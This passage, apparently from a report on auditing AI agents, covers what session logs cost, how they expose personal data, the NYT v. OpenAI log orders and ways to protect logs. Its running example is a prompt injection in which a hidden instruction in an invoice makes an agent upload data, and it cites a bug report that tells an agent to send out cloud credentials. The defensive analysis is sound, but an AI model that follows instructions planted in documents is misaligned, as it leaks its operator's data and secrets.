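The simplest remedy is to append only what is new. For call 41, the log needs the invoice's 1,500 tokens, the 500 tokens the model wrote, and a note that the model read positions 1 to 85,000. Anyone can then rebuild the exact input from the earlier entries.

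It is easy to forget to record where each model call starts and ends. Yu and colleagues recorded 194 model calls with a proxy and rebuilt the conversation in every call from what six frameworks had saved, but they took the start and end of each call from the proxy's record. Three of the frameworks also kept the system prompt in their program code instead of the saved history, so an auditor would need a copy of that prompt as it was on the day of the call.

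Some frameworks can keep only the latest snapshot of the conversation. After 200 rounds, this reduced LlamaIndex's storage from about 56 MB to 645 KB. It would work for the invoice session, because the last input contains all the earlier ones, but not for a session in which the harness had compacted the history.

Content addressing is more flexible. The software computes a hash of each block of text, stores the block once under that hash, and writes only the hash wherever the block appears again. In the invoice session, each call would need a list of hashes for the opening material and all the messages since. The 60 lists would hold 3,600 hashes of 32 bytes each, or 0.12 MB, so the log would need about 0.62 MB instead of 15.5 MB. The total size of the lists still grows with the square of the session's length, but each repeated message adds 32 bytes instead of several thousand.

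Yu and colleagues tested the method on 70 runs and reduced storage by a factor of 4.8 to 32.7, depending on the framework. All 310 files passed their checks after restoration. The method works less well on blocks that differ slightly, because it stores each version separately.

Ordinary compression handles near-copies better. With zstd, a widely used compression program, the average LangGraph store shrank by a factor of 136 and the OpenAI Agents SDK store, which had much less repetition to remove, by a factor of 14. LangGraph's store was about 15 times as large as the SDK's before compression and only 1.6 times as large afterwards. These factors are estimates of what is possible, since the researchers compressed the files as one continuous stream without building a restorable archive. An archive of this kind also has to be unpacked before anyone can search it.

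A general-purpose storage system may not find the repetition by itself. When Yu and colleagues looked for duplicate blocks in one raw LangGraph database, they found almost none. After extracting the text, they found that the same database held each piece of content about 12 times. The database splits long text across pages, and the JSON format changes some characters, so identical passages no longer match on disk.

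### What a year of logs costs

Suppose the company runs 10,000 invoice sessions a day and keeps each log for a year. It could put the logs in a searchable service or in a cheap archive.

According to AWS's *Amazon CloudWatch*, the price page for a searchable log service, loading a gigabyte costs $0.50 and storing it costs $0.03 a month after compression. One of the page's examples assumes that 30 GB of logs compress to 6 GB. On that assumption, each gigabyte costs

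$0.50 + 12 × $0.03 / 5 = $0.572

to load and keep for a year. AWS's *Amazon S3 Glacier storage classes* gives a price of $0.00099 per gigabyte a month for Deep Archive, its cheapest class, or about 1.2 cents a year. An operator has to wait 12 to 48 hours to get data back from it.

The table uses these prices without free allowances, regional differences, or the archive's charges for uploading and retrieving files.

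| Record | One session | One year | Searchable | Archive |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Metadata-only events | 0.18 MB | 0.66 TB | $380 | $8 |
| Metadata-only events and connection records | 0.22 MB | 0.80 TB | $460 | $10 |
| Session-level, each message once | 0.68 MB | 2.5 TB | $1,400 | $29 |
| Session-level, full input at every call | 15.7 MB | 57 TB | $33,000 | $680 |
| Token-level, each token once | 0.50 MB | 1.8 TB | $1,000 | $22 |
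| Token-level, each token once, with 20 alternatives | 5.3 MB | 19 TB | $11,000 | $230 |
| Token-level, full input at every call | 15.5 MB | 57 TB | $32,000 | $670 |
| Token-level, full input, with 20 alternatives | 20.3 MB | 74 TB | $42,000 | $880 |

Cost depends far more on whether the log repeats its text than on whether it records tokens or messages. A session-level log that saves the full input at every call costs about 31 times as much as a token-level log that stores each token once. The basic token-level log is slightly cheaper than the session-level log without repetition, because the estimate includes no event metadata for the token-level log. In a searchable service, the token-level log would be somewhat larger than shown, since the service would probably store the identifiers as text.

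Yu and colleagues found a similar gap. At 10,000 tasks a day, LangGraph's default settings would produce 51 GB daily. Keeping only the newest checkpoint would reduce this to 3.1 GB and still preserve the whole conversation, but the operator could no longer return to an earlier checkpoint.

The cost also depends on how the records are stored. A company could keep the metadata searchable and archive the tokens, with 20 alternatives each, for about $610 a year, less than half the price of keeping session-level text searchable. But an investigator who spotted the upload in the metadata would have to wait at least half a day to read the invoice behind it.

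AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP03 Implement structured logging and comprehensive audit trails* recommends keeping debugging logs for 7 to 14 days, operational logs for 30 to 90 days and compliance logs for one to seven years, and claims that separate periods cut storage cost substantially. But at the prices above, loading accounts for 87% of the first year's cost, so deleting a log after 14 days would save only about 12%. The saving is larger for logs that would otherwise be kept for many years, because over seven years storage costs about as much as loading.

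Operators can halve the loading charge to $0.25 per gigabyte by choosing a log class with fewer features, according to AWS re:Post's *Understanding CloudWatch Costs*. AWS's *Amazon CloudWatch Logs announces intelligent tiering for storage* (2026) describes a feature that may also reduce storage charges without much effort, by moving rarely used logs to cheaper tiers while keeping them searchable. Other features add to the bill, such as scanning for sensitive data, which costs $0.12 per gigabyte, or about $300 a year for the session-level text.

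### How much recording slows the agent

Writing a record takes very little time compared with a model call. Shah and Kathrotia timed 20,000 records and found median delays between 12.5 and 81.6 microseconds, depending on the type of event. At the slowest median, 180 records would delay the invoice session by about 15 milliseconds.

Saving to a database takes longer. *Persona-Execution Separation* (2026) reports a median of 6.34 milliseconds for an audit write in a working product, based on 20 writes. At that speed, 180 records would take 1.1 seconds, or about 0.04% of a 50-minute session. This delay is short enough to justify having the harness wait until a record is stored before it executes the tool call. Without this wait, a crash could leave the upload in call 41 with no record.

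Token-level logging also adds little overhead. *Benchmarking LLM Serving Systems for Agentic AI Workloads with XPerf* (Wang, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) reports on agents that were recorded so that the same work could be replayed on different servers. Tracing the calls added 0.1% to response time, and the software that collected the traces used less than 5% of one processor core and 2 GB of memory. The token identifiers added 250 KB of data per second. XPerf saves the input of every call. Its traces averaged 4.6 MB per user request and reached 27 MB, so the 15.5 MB estimated for the invoice session is plausible.

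At 10,000 sessions a day, full-input logging would write about 1.8 MB per second, which an ordinary disk can handle. The XPerf test did not measure the overhead of having the server return alternative tokens. The host probes described earlier add about 3% to the agent's running time, more than any of these methods.

Small records can still be useful. Shah and Kathrotia ran 240 tests, half of them with planted faults. Their full records revealed 98.3% of the faults, compared with 23.3% for records in the OpenTelemetry format. The researchers chose both the faults and the fields that would expose them, so real incidents would probably be harder to detect.

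### What it costs to have a model read the logs

According to AWS re:Post, a query costs $0.005 per gigabyte scanned, and it scans everything in the chosen logs and period. Searching a year of session-level logs for "verify-suppliers.example" would cost about $12, or $286 if the logs repeated the full input at every call.

A search finds only what the investigator thinks to look for, so someone has to read the session to find anything unexpected. At 240 words a minute, a person would take about six and a half hours to read its 125,000 tokens.

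A model is faster, but the bill adds up. *Insights Generator* (2026) gives Anthropic's list prices for two models. Claude Opus 4.6 costs $5 per million input tokens and $25 per million output tokens, and the smaller Claude Haiku 4.5 costs $1 and $5. Anthropic has since released newer models, whose prices may differ. If the reader writes 1,000 tokens about each session, including its reasoning, Opus 4.6 costs

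0.125 × $5 + 0.001 × $25 = $0.65 per session.

| | One session | One day (10,000 sessions) | One year |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading with Claude Opus 4.6 | $0.65 | $6,500 | $2.4 million |
| Reading with Claude Haiku 4.5 | $0.13 | $1,300 | $470,000 |
| Searchable storage of session-level text for a year | $0.0004 | $4 | $1,400 |

Even with the cheaper model, reading a session once costs more than 300 times as much as storing it for a year. Reading one day's sessions costs almost as much as storing a year's sessions.

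Repeated text is even more expensive to read than to store. Having Opus 4.6 read the full input of all 60 calls would cost $19.20 per session before discounts. *Beyond Token Savings* (2026) notes that commercial providers charge less for input they have recently processed, which would reduce the bill but not eliminate it. It is better to remove the repetition before the model reads the records.

Some repetition remains even when the log stores each message once, because agents often read the same files several times. *TraceLite* (2026) found considerable overlap among the tool results in coding sessions. Its method removes overlapping text and turns older text into images, which reduced the agent's input by 33% and its API cost by 21%. An operator could shorten logs in the same way before a model reads them, but should keep the originals because the shortened version is not an exact record.

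Running the agent costs more than reading its logs. At Opus 4.6 prices, each session of the invoice agent would cost $19.20 for input and $0.75 for output. Even if discounts cut the input price by 90%, a year of sessions would cost almost $10 million. The most expensive log in the storage table, at $42,000, would add about 0.4% to that.

Models can also look for patterns across many sessions. *Insights Generator* compared five systems that do this, and their average cost ranged from about $5 to $44 per analysis. Costs rose with session length. One system averaged about $17 on one set of runs and $71 on another with longer records.

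A model can also check each action before the harness executes it. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) reports tests in which a model took 1.2 seconds per decision, while fixed rules took less than 10 milliseconds for a whole run. The rules decided all but 3.1% of actions, which went to the model. Checking all 60 tool calls in the invoice session with a model would add 72 seconds, but checking 3.1% of them would add about two seconds on average.

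The same filter would not save much if every flagged action led a model to read the entire session. If the rules flagged 3.1% of actions at random, the chance that a session of 60 tool calls contained at least one would be

1 − 0.969⁶⁰ ≈ 85%.

The model could instead read only the text around the flagged action. For call 41, the opening instructions, the invoice and the agent's output come to 7,000 tokens, which Opus 4.6 could review for about 6 cents. But if the agent had read the malicious invoice in call 10 and acted on it in call 41, the text around call 41 would include the upload but not the instruction that caused it.

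## Personal data, secrets and confidentiality in the records

Much of the text in an agent's log is other people's information. The log copies whatever the agent read, including material that no auditor will ever need, and anyone who can open the log can read it. This gives an operator a better reason to limit logging than storage cost does, since text is cheap to store.

### What a detailed log collects

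In the invoice session, the 60 tool results might include the names and phone numbers of suppliers' staff, the bank details of self-employed contractors and the prices each supplier charges. An investigator looking into call 41 needs the text of one invoice, but a full-content log holds the text of all 60 results.

Prices recorded in an agent's logs may be trade secrets. EU and US law protect a trade secret only if its owner takes reasonable steps to keep it secret. A company that restricts access to its price database but lets every developer search the agent's logs has a weaker claim to that protection.

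Passwords and access keys also get into logs. *Clawed and Dangerous* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that a developer asks to summarise bug reports. One report contains hidden instructions to read the file that stores the developer's cloud credentials and send its contents to an outside address. The agent runs with the developer's permissions, so each step looks like ordinary work. If the harness records tool results, the log also contains the credentials, and anyone who steals it could use them to get into the same cloud account.

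Secrets are harder to remove from logs that repeat their text. If the invoice agent read a password in the result of tool call 10, the password would be in the input of calls 11 to 60. A log that saves the full input of every call would contain it at least 50 times, and deleting one entry would leave the other copies.

A chain of thought can also contain personal data that was in none of the source files. The model might notice that two of a supplier's invoices were late and that an email mentioned a hospital, and write that the supplier's owner seems seriously ill. The guess may be wrong, and nobody asked for it, but the log keeps it next to the owner's name. Under European law, an inference about someone's health can count as health data, which has stricter protection than most personal data.

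The three levels of log expose different things:

| Information | Token-level log | Session-level log with content | Network-plus-model log |
|---|---|---|---|
| Personal data in prompts and files | Yes | Yes | Only with decryption or the content of model calls |
| Passwords and access keys | If the model read or wrote them | If they were in a tool call or its result | With decryption, including logins the model never saw |
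| Inferences about people | Yes, in the full reasoning | Often only in a summary | Only with the content of model calls |
| Sites contacted, and when | Only if the text mentions them | As the harness reported them | Yes, even without decryption |

Storing text as token numbers does not hide it, because anyone with the tokenizer can convert the numbers back. If an operator removes a name from the recorded output but keeps the list of the 20 most likely tokens at each position, the name will usually still be among them.

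Network records without content can be sensitive too. If an employee uses a company's general-purpose assistant to book a medical appointment, the records might show a name lookup for an addiction clinic at 22:14, followed by a connection from that employee's session. This suggests that the employee is seeking addiction treatment, even though the records contain none of the conversation. Li and colleagues found that traffic patterns can often show what kind of work an agent is doing even when the destinations are masked.

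### Data-protection limits on logging

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) applies to information relating to a person who could reasonably be identified. Security can be a legitimate reason to process such data in audit logs, and organisations must be able to demonstrate that they comply with the regulation, for which they often need records. But Article 5 requires them to collect personal data for a specified purpose, limit it to what is necessary for that purpose (data minimisation), and keep it in identifiable form no longer than necessary (storage limitation).

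These rules are hard to reconcile with recording everything in case it proves useful. For the invoice agent, the purpose might be to investigate unauthorized transfers. That could justify keeping the text of outside documents for as long as such transfers usually take to discover, but it would not justify keeping every clerk's prompts for ten years. If managers later used the log to compare how fast the clerks worked, the company would have to justify that new purpose separately.

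In 2021, France's data-protection authority, the CNIL, recommended keeping logs of who used a system for six months to a year in most cases. This is compatible with the AI Act's six-month minimum, but the recommendation was meant for ordinary access logs, which contain far less text than a record of an agent's session.

In a December 2024 opinion on AI models, the European Data Protection Board, which brings together the EU's national regulators, concluded that a model trained on personal data is not automatically anonymous. It said regulators should assess how likely it is that someone could extract the data. The question is much simpler for a log, because the log contains the text itself. *AI Privacy Risks & Mitigations – Large Language Models*, an expert report the Board published in 2025, also covers the data that flows through a system in use, including prompts and outputs.

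People also have a right to a copy of their data, normally within one month. If a supplier's bookkeeper asked what the company held about her, the answer could include passages from the agent's logs. Searching the logs for her name would take little effort, but having someone read the results and remove other people's data would take much more.

The right of access can also cover audit records. In a 2023 case about a Finnish bank, the EU's Court of Justice held that a customer was entitled to know when and why staff had looked at his data, but not normally which employees had done so. If an agent consults customer files, its operator may need to tell customers when and why it did. A metadata-only log would be enough for this if it recorded the customer, the time and the purpose.

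### When someone asks for erasure

Article 17 of the GDPR lets people have their data erased in several situations, such as when the organisation no longer needs it. It exempts data that the organisation needs to meet an obligation under EU or national law, or to bring or defend a legal claim.

Suppose a high-risk recruitment agent rejects an applicant on 1 March 2028, and the applicant asks for erasure on 1 May. The AI Act's minimum retention period would run until 1 September. The two laws are slightly circular, because the GDPR's right to erasure has an exception for legal obligations, while the AI Act's minimum gives way to data-protection law. The employer could reasonably keep the log that Article 12 requires until September, restrict who can open it, and then delete it. It would have a weak case for keeping debugging files, duplicate inputs or reasoning text that were not needed for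 that log.

If the applicant threatened to sue, the exception for legal claims could justify keeping the relevant session for longer, but a general worry about future lawsuits would not justify keeping every session.

No AI Act duty applies to the invoice agent. Tax law may require the company to keep invoice 8841 for years, but not a second copy in the agent's log. If the supplier's bookkeeper asked for erasure, the company would have to show that it still needed that copy for security.

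A foreign court order does not count as an obligation under EU or national law. A company with European users could therefore receive a deletion request under the GDPR and an order from a US court to keep the same data. OpenAI warned of this kind of conflict in 2025.

### The order to preserve deleted chats

The New York Times sued OpenAI and Microsoft for copyright infringement in December 2023, and other publishers and authors brought related cases. The publishers wanted ChatGPT's output logs to find out how often it reproduced their articles or replaced the need to read them. But OpenAI was deleting some of those logs, either at users' request or under its normal retention rules.

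In January 2025, Magistrate Judge Ona Wang refused the publishers' request that OpenAI preserve all the logs. She asked whether OpenAI could instead separate or anonymise the chats that users wanted deleted. OpenAI replied that it was reluctant to preserve everything, citing its users' wishes and privacy laws around the world.

The publishers asked again, with evidence that a significant number of chats had been deleted. On 13 May, in *In re OpenAI, Inc., Copyright Infringement Litigation*, Judge Wang (2025) directed OpenAI to preserve and segregate all output log data that it would otherwise delete, even when a user asked for the deletion or a privacy law required it. She noted that OpenAI still had not said whether it would take such steps without an order.

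In a letter the next day, OpenAI (2025) argued that the order would make it disregard legal and contractual commitments to hundreds of millions of people, and to businesses and governments. Judge Wang declined to reconsider. According to Maatman, Donoho and Ryan (2025), in *New York Federal Court’s OpenAI Discovery Orders Provide Key Insights For Companies*, she thought it was too early to decide whether the burden was proportionate or whether the deletions would bias a sample.

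The publishers' best argument was that deletions could bias the evidence. If people who use ChatGPT to get around a paywall are more likely to delete their chats, the remaining chats will understate how often this happens. District Judge Sidney Stein upheld the order on 26 June. Bloomberg Law's *OpenAI Fails To Pare Back Order To Preserve User Data* (2025) reports that he considered it a "permissible inference" that some users delete chats because they may be infringing copyright. That is plausible, but people also delete chats about their health, families and work, and the inference doesn't establish how common each reason is. A random sample of deleted chats might have settled the question while affecting far fewer people.

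According to OpenAI's *How we’re responding to The New York Times’ data demands* (2025), the order covered the API as well as consumer ChatGPT, but not ChatGPT Enterprise, ChatGPT Edu or API customers with a zero-retention agreement. A company whose agent used the API without such an agreement in the summer of 2025 could have had its prompts retained because of a lawsuit it had no part in.

The two sides negotiated an end to the order, and the court approved their agreement on 9 October 2025. OpenAI's duty to preserve new data ended as of 26 September. Maatman and colleagues explain that OpenAI still had to keep the logs it had already segregated, except those from the European Economic Area, Switzerland and the UK, and to continue preserving data from certain listed accounts.

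In an update that October, OpenAI said the remaining material was a limited set of user data from April to September 2025 and that only a small legal and security team could open it. The data probably starts in April because OpenAI can take up to 30 days to delete a chat after a request, so some of April's deletions were still pending when the order arrived in May.

### The order to produce 20 million chats

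The production dispute concerned a different set of chats. The publishers first asked for 1.4 billion chats and later for 120 million, and OpenAI offered a sample of 20 million. The court said the sample was less than 0.05% of the logs OpenAI had preserved. According to the law firm Anderson Kill, the sample covers consumer chats from December 2022 to November 2024 and excludes deleted chats, temporary chats and Enterprise accounts. It therefore doesn't include the chats that the May order saved from deletion.

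In October 2025, OpenAI proposed to search the sample and hand over only the chats that involved the publishers' work. Judge Wang rejected the proposal in November and ordered OpenAI to produce all 20 million chats. In its appeal, OpenAI (2025) argued that this would disclose almost 20 million private conversations for no legitimate purpose, because the publishers had conceded that more than 99.99% of the chats had nothing to do with their claims of infringing output. By that figure, fewer than 2,000 chats were relevant to those claims.

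In Fox News' *OpenAI accuses NY Times of wanting to invade millions of users' privacy*, a Times spokesperson replied that no user's privacy was at risk. OpenAI had anonymised the chats itself, and a protective order limited what the publishers could do with them.

Judge Stein upheld the production order on 5 January 2026. Lee (2026) summarises his reasons in *OpenAI Loses Privacy Gambit*. Judge Stein reasoned that chats containing none of the publishers' text can still be relevant to OpenAI's fair use defence, because they help show whether ChatGPT competes with news articles. He accepted that users had a sincere interest in privacy but thought three safeguards protected it: the small size of the sample, the removal of identifying details and the protective order. He also distinguished the chats from wiretapped phone calls, because users had voluntarily sent their messages to OpenAI. He wrote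 that Judge Wang's rulings were "neither clearly erroneous nor contrary to law" (quoted in ABA Journal, *ChatGPT creator must turn over 20M chat logs in copyright litigation*).

The court has the better argument on relevance. Calculating how often ChatGPT replaces a news article requires the conversations that don't match the search as well as those that do, and a keyword search could miss a close paraphrase.

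The safeguards are easier to question. *Judge Orders OpenAI To Give Lawyers 20 Million Private Chats*, a commentary critical of the ruling, argues that researchers can often link supposedly anonymous data back to individuals. Chats are especially vulnerable because people often describe themselves when they write. A message that mentions a small town, an unusual job and a recent divorce may identify its author without a name. The protective order means fewer people might try to identify someone, but it does not make the chats anonymous.

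OpenAI complied. *Reporting the facts about the New York Times’ lawsuit*, its running account of the case, says that the company masked personal details and set up access controls to stop the Times from copying or printing irrelevant data. OpenAI also complains there that the Times and Judge Wang relied on Anthropic's willingness to produce five million conversations in another lawsuit.

In March 2026, Judge Wang ordered OpenAI to produce another 88 million output logs, according to Bloomberg Law's *New York Times Wins Bid for OpenAI President’s Diary in IP Suit* (2026). The logs date from before OpenAI introduced a filter to stop its models from repeating protected text.

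On 9 July, the publishers asked the court to punish OpenAI for deleting chat logs and for concealing, over two years, that it had tools to search for their content (Moreno, 2026, *OpenAI Accused Of Hiding Evidence In NYT Copyright Fight*). In AsiaOne's *News outlets urge a judge to sanction OpenAI* (2026), OpenAI calls the allegations false and accuses the Times of continuing to invade the privacy of people not involved in the case. The Russian technology site iXBT.com (2026) reports a further allegation that OpenAI made the data it handed over unfit for analysis.

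According to Moreno (2026), in *OpenAI Fights Sanctions Bid In News Copyright MDL*, the sanctions could bar OpenAI from relying on the 20 million chats in its defence. On 14 August, the company argued that it had not violated a preservation order or misrepresented its ability to search. OpenAI's running account of the case lists several later filings but no decision on sanctions. The main question, whether training on the articles was fair use, was still undecided on 2 November 2026, according to Rijo (2026), in *OpenAI quotes 20 briefs, US government included, against New York Times*.

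The case shows operators that a court can require access to logs, whatever purpose they were kept for. The 20 million chats were available because OpenAI had kept them. Ryan Kriger, a lecturer at the University of Vermont, argues in Bloomberg Law's *OpenAI’s Privacy Bet in Copyright Suit Puts Chatbots on Alert* that limiting how long a company keeps data is a big part of data minimisation.

### What model providers keep

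An operator's own log is often not the only copy. OpenAI's published terms, as of October 2025, gave these periods:

| Service | What OpenAI kept |
|---|---|
| Consumer ChatGPT | Chats until the user deletes them, then up to 30 days |
| ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu | As long as the customer's administrators choose, then up to 30 days after deletion |
| API | Inputs and outputs in logs for 30 days; stored conversations and files for as long as the customer's settings provide |
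| API with zero data retention | No inputs or outputs |

These terms make an exception where the law requires OpenAI to keep data, and OpenAI can also keep deleted ChatGPT chats longer for security reasons. Darinor's engineering guide *How to Build an Agent Audit Trail Before You Need It* (September 2026) still gives 30 days as OpenAI's default retention period for the API.

Zero retention can have safety exceptions. According to its 2025 developer documentation, OpenAI would keep images for human review if its scanner flagged them as possible child sexual abuse material, even for customers with zero retention. Anthropic's terms that year allowed it to keep inputs and outputs for up to two years if they broke its usage policy, and its safety classifier scores for up to seven. It could still keep some of these safety results for customers with a zero-retention agreement. Providers change these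 terms, so an operator should save a copy of the ones that applied when each session ran.

Zero retention protects people whose data appears in the text, but it removes a copy that the operator cannot alter. Dai and colleagues checked their outside record against the provider's copies, which would not exist under zero retention. In the invoice session, the operator's log might be the only evidence that call 41 contained the hidden instruction, and an auditor would have to trust that nobody had edited it.

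Ordinary retention is also short, so if the company discovered the upload 45 days later, the API copy would already be gone. Darinor therefore recommends that operators save each input themselves just before the harness sends it, in storage that the agent cannot rewrite.

### Five ways to limit what a log reveals

An operator can remove sensitive text, hide it from most readers, encrypt it, restrict access to it, or keep only a hash of it. The table compares these methods in four situations.

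| Method | Someone steals the log | A court orders production | A person requests erasure | An investigator needs the hidden instruction |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Redaction when writing | The thief gets what the software missed | The operator has only the redacted text | Only missed details remain | Available unless the software removed it |
| Redaction when reading | The thief gets everything | The original is available | The operator must delete the original | Available |
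| Encryption with deletable keys | The thief needs the keys too | The operator can decrypt it while the key exists | The operator deletes the key | Available while the key exists |
| Restricted access | Theft is harder, but the thief gets everything | The original is available | The operator must delete the original | Available to authorized staff |
| Hash in place of text | The thief can guess short or predictable text | The operator has only the hash | The hash may still be personal data | Unavailable unless a copy turns up |

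### Redaction

Redaction software searches text for names, addresses, account numbers and similar details, and replaces them with labels such as "[PERSON]". If it runs before the harness saves an entry, the sensitive text never reaches the log. But the operator cannot recover the removed text, which may include evidence. In the invoice session, the software might mistake the address in the hidden instruction for a supplier's contact details and replace it with a label. An investigator could not then match the instruction to the destination of the upload.

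Many access keys have a fixed prefix and length, so software can find them with a simple pattern. A password in an ordinary sentence is harder to find because it can look like any other word, and the software has no pattern for trade secrets.

Some of the best measurements of how accurately software finds identifying details come from medical records, because researchers have collections of notes in which people have marked those details. In *De-identification of Patient Notes with Recurrent Neural Networks* (2017), Dernoncourt, Lee and colleagues reported that their system found about 97% of the details in one collection and about 99% in another. Newer systems may do better, but an agent's log is more varied than a hospital note and can include code, tables, several languages and text that an attacker wrote to confuse software.

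Small error rates still leave a lot of data. Suppose each invoice session contains 20 personal details, and the software misses each one independently. With 10,000 sessions a day, the results would be:

| Details found | Details missed per day | Sessions with nothing missed |
|---|---|---|
| 97% | 6,000 | 0.97²⁰ ≈ 54% |
| 99% | 2,000 | 0.99²⁰ ≈ 82% |
| 99.9% | 200 | 0.999²⁰ ≈ 98% |

The errors would cluster, because software that misses an unusual name once will probably miss it again. An operator should measure the error rate on a sample of its own logs, and count missed sensitive details separately from harmless words that the software removed. Overall accuracy can be high even when the software misses many sensitive details, because most words in a log are not sensitive.

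Redaction when reading leaves the original in place and shows most readers a masked version. This avoids losing evidence, and the operator can improve the redaction software later and apply it to old entries. A developer fixing a bug might see "[PERSON]" while an investigator with permission sees the name. But a thief, a court or a dishonest administrator could still get the full text, and for data-protection purposes the operator still holds all of it.

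Restricted access has the same limits. OpenAI's small legal team and the protective order in the Times case meant that fewer people could read the chats, but those who did could still learn just as much from them.

### Encrypted content with deletable keys

Erasure is awkward for a tamper-evident log, because removing an entry looks like tampering. An operator can avoid this conflict by storing the text separately from the record of events:

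1. The harness encrypts each message or tool result with its own random key.
2. It saves the encrypted text, and puts a hash of that encrypted text in the tamper-evident log along with the time, the tool and other metadata.
3. It saves the key in a separate store that log readers cannot open directly.
4. When the retention period ends or a valid erasure request arrives, the operator deletes the key.

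When the operator deletes a document's key, the encrypted text becomes unreadable, but the log still passes its checks because no entry has changed. An auditor can still see, for example, that the agent read the document at 10:42 and that the operator later deleted the key.

The keys take little space. The invoice session has 120 model outputs and tool results, each with a 32-byte key, so its keys take 3,840 bytes. The keys for a year of sessions take about 14 GB, compared with 2.5 TB for the session-level log.

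With a single key for the whole session, erasing one supplier's details would also destroy the other suppliers' invoices and the evidence about call 41. Separate keys are less simple but mostly avoid this. They do not help when one document names several people, or when the model repeats a name in later messages. The operator also needs an index of which messages concern which person, and that index is itself personal data.

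The method also works only if the operator deletes every copy of the key, including backups. Any names in the unencrypted metadata remain readable. Once a lawsuit begins, deleting a key can amount to destroying evidence. Maatman and colleagues advise companies to build systems that can pause deletion by user, region or product line. Separate keys make this easier, since the operator can keep the keys for the disputed sessions and continue to delete the others.

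### Why a plain hash protects so little

Darinor points out that an investigator can use a hash to verify which input the model received, but needs the saved input to work out what happened. If the operator had kept only a hash of invoice 8841, an investigator could confirm that a copy from the supplier was the same document, but could not discover the hidden instruction without such a copy.

Operators also use hashes to disguise identifiers, so that they can tell which entries concern the same person without storing a name or number. This works badly for short identifiers. A nine-digit number, such as a US Social Security number, has only

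10⁹ = 1,000,000,000

possible values. Someone who steals the log can hash all of them with the same public method and look for a match. A modern graphics card can compute more than a billion SHA-256 hashes per second, so the search takes less than a second. Even a slow program that tries a million values per second would finish in about 17 minutes.

The thief can also save the results in a table, with a 32-byte hash and a 4-byte number for every possible value. The table would take up 36 GB, and the thief could use it to look up every identifier in the log.

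Adding a different random value, called a salt, to each identifier before hashing makes such a table useless. But the operator normally stores the salt beside the hash, so the thief can still search for each identifier separately. At a billion attempts per second, finding a million identifiers would take at most 11.6 days. Salting also gives the same person a different hash in each entry, so the operator can no longer link the entries.

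A keyed hash, such as HMAC-SHA-256, mixes a secret key into the calculation. A random 256-bit key has about 10⁷⁷ possible values, so a thief who has only the log cannot test the nine-digit numbers. The operator can still link entries, because the same identifier and key always produce the same hash. But a thief who also gets the key can test the numbers as quickly as before, so the operator has to store the key away from the log.

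When a log replaces clerks' IDs with keyed hashes, the GDPR treats the data as pseudonymous, not anonymous, as long as the operator can use the key to link it to a person. The data is safer but still subject to the rules on access and erasure. Activity patterns can also identify someone. If sessions under one hash start at 06:00 every day and only one clerk works that early, colleagues will know who it is. Using a new key each month limits how long anyone can follow such a pattern, but an investigator will need both keys to trace a clerk across two months.

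Hashes of longer text can have the same weakness if most of the text is predictable. Suppose a thief knows everything on a supplier's invoice except an amount between $0.00 and $99,999.99. With a plain hash of the invoice, the thief could find the amount almost immediately by testing all ten million possibilities. The deletable-key method avoids this by hashing the encrypted text. If the log also kept a plain hash of the original, a thief could still test guesses after the operator had deleted the key.

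## Setting rules for capture, retention and protection

A more detailed log gives investigators more evidence but also collects more personal data. An operator can settle how much to record in four steps:

1. List what the agent can reach, and which of its possible actions nobody could undo.
2. Choose the questions that someone must be able to answer about those actions.
3. Pick the least detailed record that answers them.
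4. Decide how long to keep the record, how to protect it and who may read it.

### From the agent's reach to the questions

The first step should be to assess the agent's tools and permissions, because its task description is a poor guide to risk. In June 2026, an OpenAI agent researching public medical spending gained unauthorized access to files on a statistics portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance programme, according to Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026). The task sounded harmless, but the agent could write its own requests and send them to outside servers.

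Few companies have a complete register of their agents. SC Media recommends starting with a manual list of the agents involved in high-consequence work, recording each agent's identity, permitted tools and owner. The operator can then mark which actions are reversible. For example, the company that runs the invoice agent can correct a wrong reconciliation but cannot recall a supplier list after an upload.

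The questions in the second step have to be precise. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao, 2026) argues that nobody can check a claim about an agent until the operator has fixed four things: the policy and its version, the actions and period covered, the records required and who writes them, and the rule for reaching a verdict. "Our agent is safe" fails this test. A better claim is that in September 2026 the invoice agent uploaded files only to addresses on version 4 of the company's approved list.

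An auditor could check that claim against the log of a proxy that the network team runs, with a separate login for each session. A single upload to any other address would contradict the claim. To support it, the auditor would also need evidence that the proxy had captured every upload. Without that evidence, the verdict would be "undecidable", and the auditor would name the missing record. The upload in call 41 contradicts the claim, and the auditor can establish this from the session and destination without reading any text.

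An operator that relies on human approvals should have a system outside the agent's control record them, along with the exact action each one covers. In a hypothetical teaching example from Zhao, a firm claims that a person approves every external email. The agent's log contains a confirmation for one email, but it comes from the agent's own chat window, and the separate server that issues permissions has no approval for that recipient and attachment. The confirmation shows only that the agent's software recorded a click under someone's account.

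### Records for three deployments

The table applies the procedure to an assistant that only reads public documents, the invoice agent, and a research agent that can write and run code. The retention periods are judgements for these examples and do not override any legal minimum.

| | Document assistant | Invoice agent | Research agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| What it can reach | A fixed library of public documents | Invoices, payment records, supplier files and the web | Any program it writes, and the internet |
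| What nobody can undo | Very little | An upload of company data | An attack on another organisation |
| Questions to answer | Which documents did an answer draw on? | Who started the session, what did the agent read, and what did it send where? | The same, plus which programs ran and whether the transcript is genuine |
| Routine record | Metadata-only session log, with document versions and a keyed hash of each reply | Every tool call with its arguments and approval, a pointer to each invoice, and proxy records | Full session text, process and file events, and decrypted proxy traffic |
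| Full text | Never | In a 30-day buffer, and longer for selected sessions | For every session |
| Kept for | 30 days | 13 months, or 6 months for saved full text | 13 months |
| Main reason | A user who complains can supply the reply | The accounting system already holds the invoices | The agent could alter records on its own machine, and victims may take months to notice |

Such a small log is enough for the document assistant only because its library is fixed. If the assistant had a general web tool, it could access about as much as the agent in the Medicare case.

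For the invoice agent, the routine log stores each invoice's number and a keyed hash of the original file. An investigator can fetch the invoice from the accounting system and check it against the hash, so the log doesn't need a second copy of every supplier's bank details. This works only if the accounting system keeps the original file, because a scan of the printed page would lose an instruction hidden in white text.

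The research agent needs combined network and model records because the code it runs might interfere with the harness's log. The operator should also keep the exact tokens if it hosts the model, or the encrypted reasoning blocks if it does not.

The operator should write down why it made these choices, including why it decided not to record certain data. In Help Net Security's *Shadow AI incident response begins with logs that may already be gone*, Brandy Wityak of the security company LevelBlue says companies with documented reasons for leaving out a control are better placed when a regulator asks about it. A document that identifies a risk but records no decision about it can count against the company.

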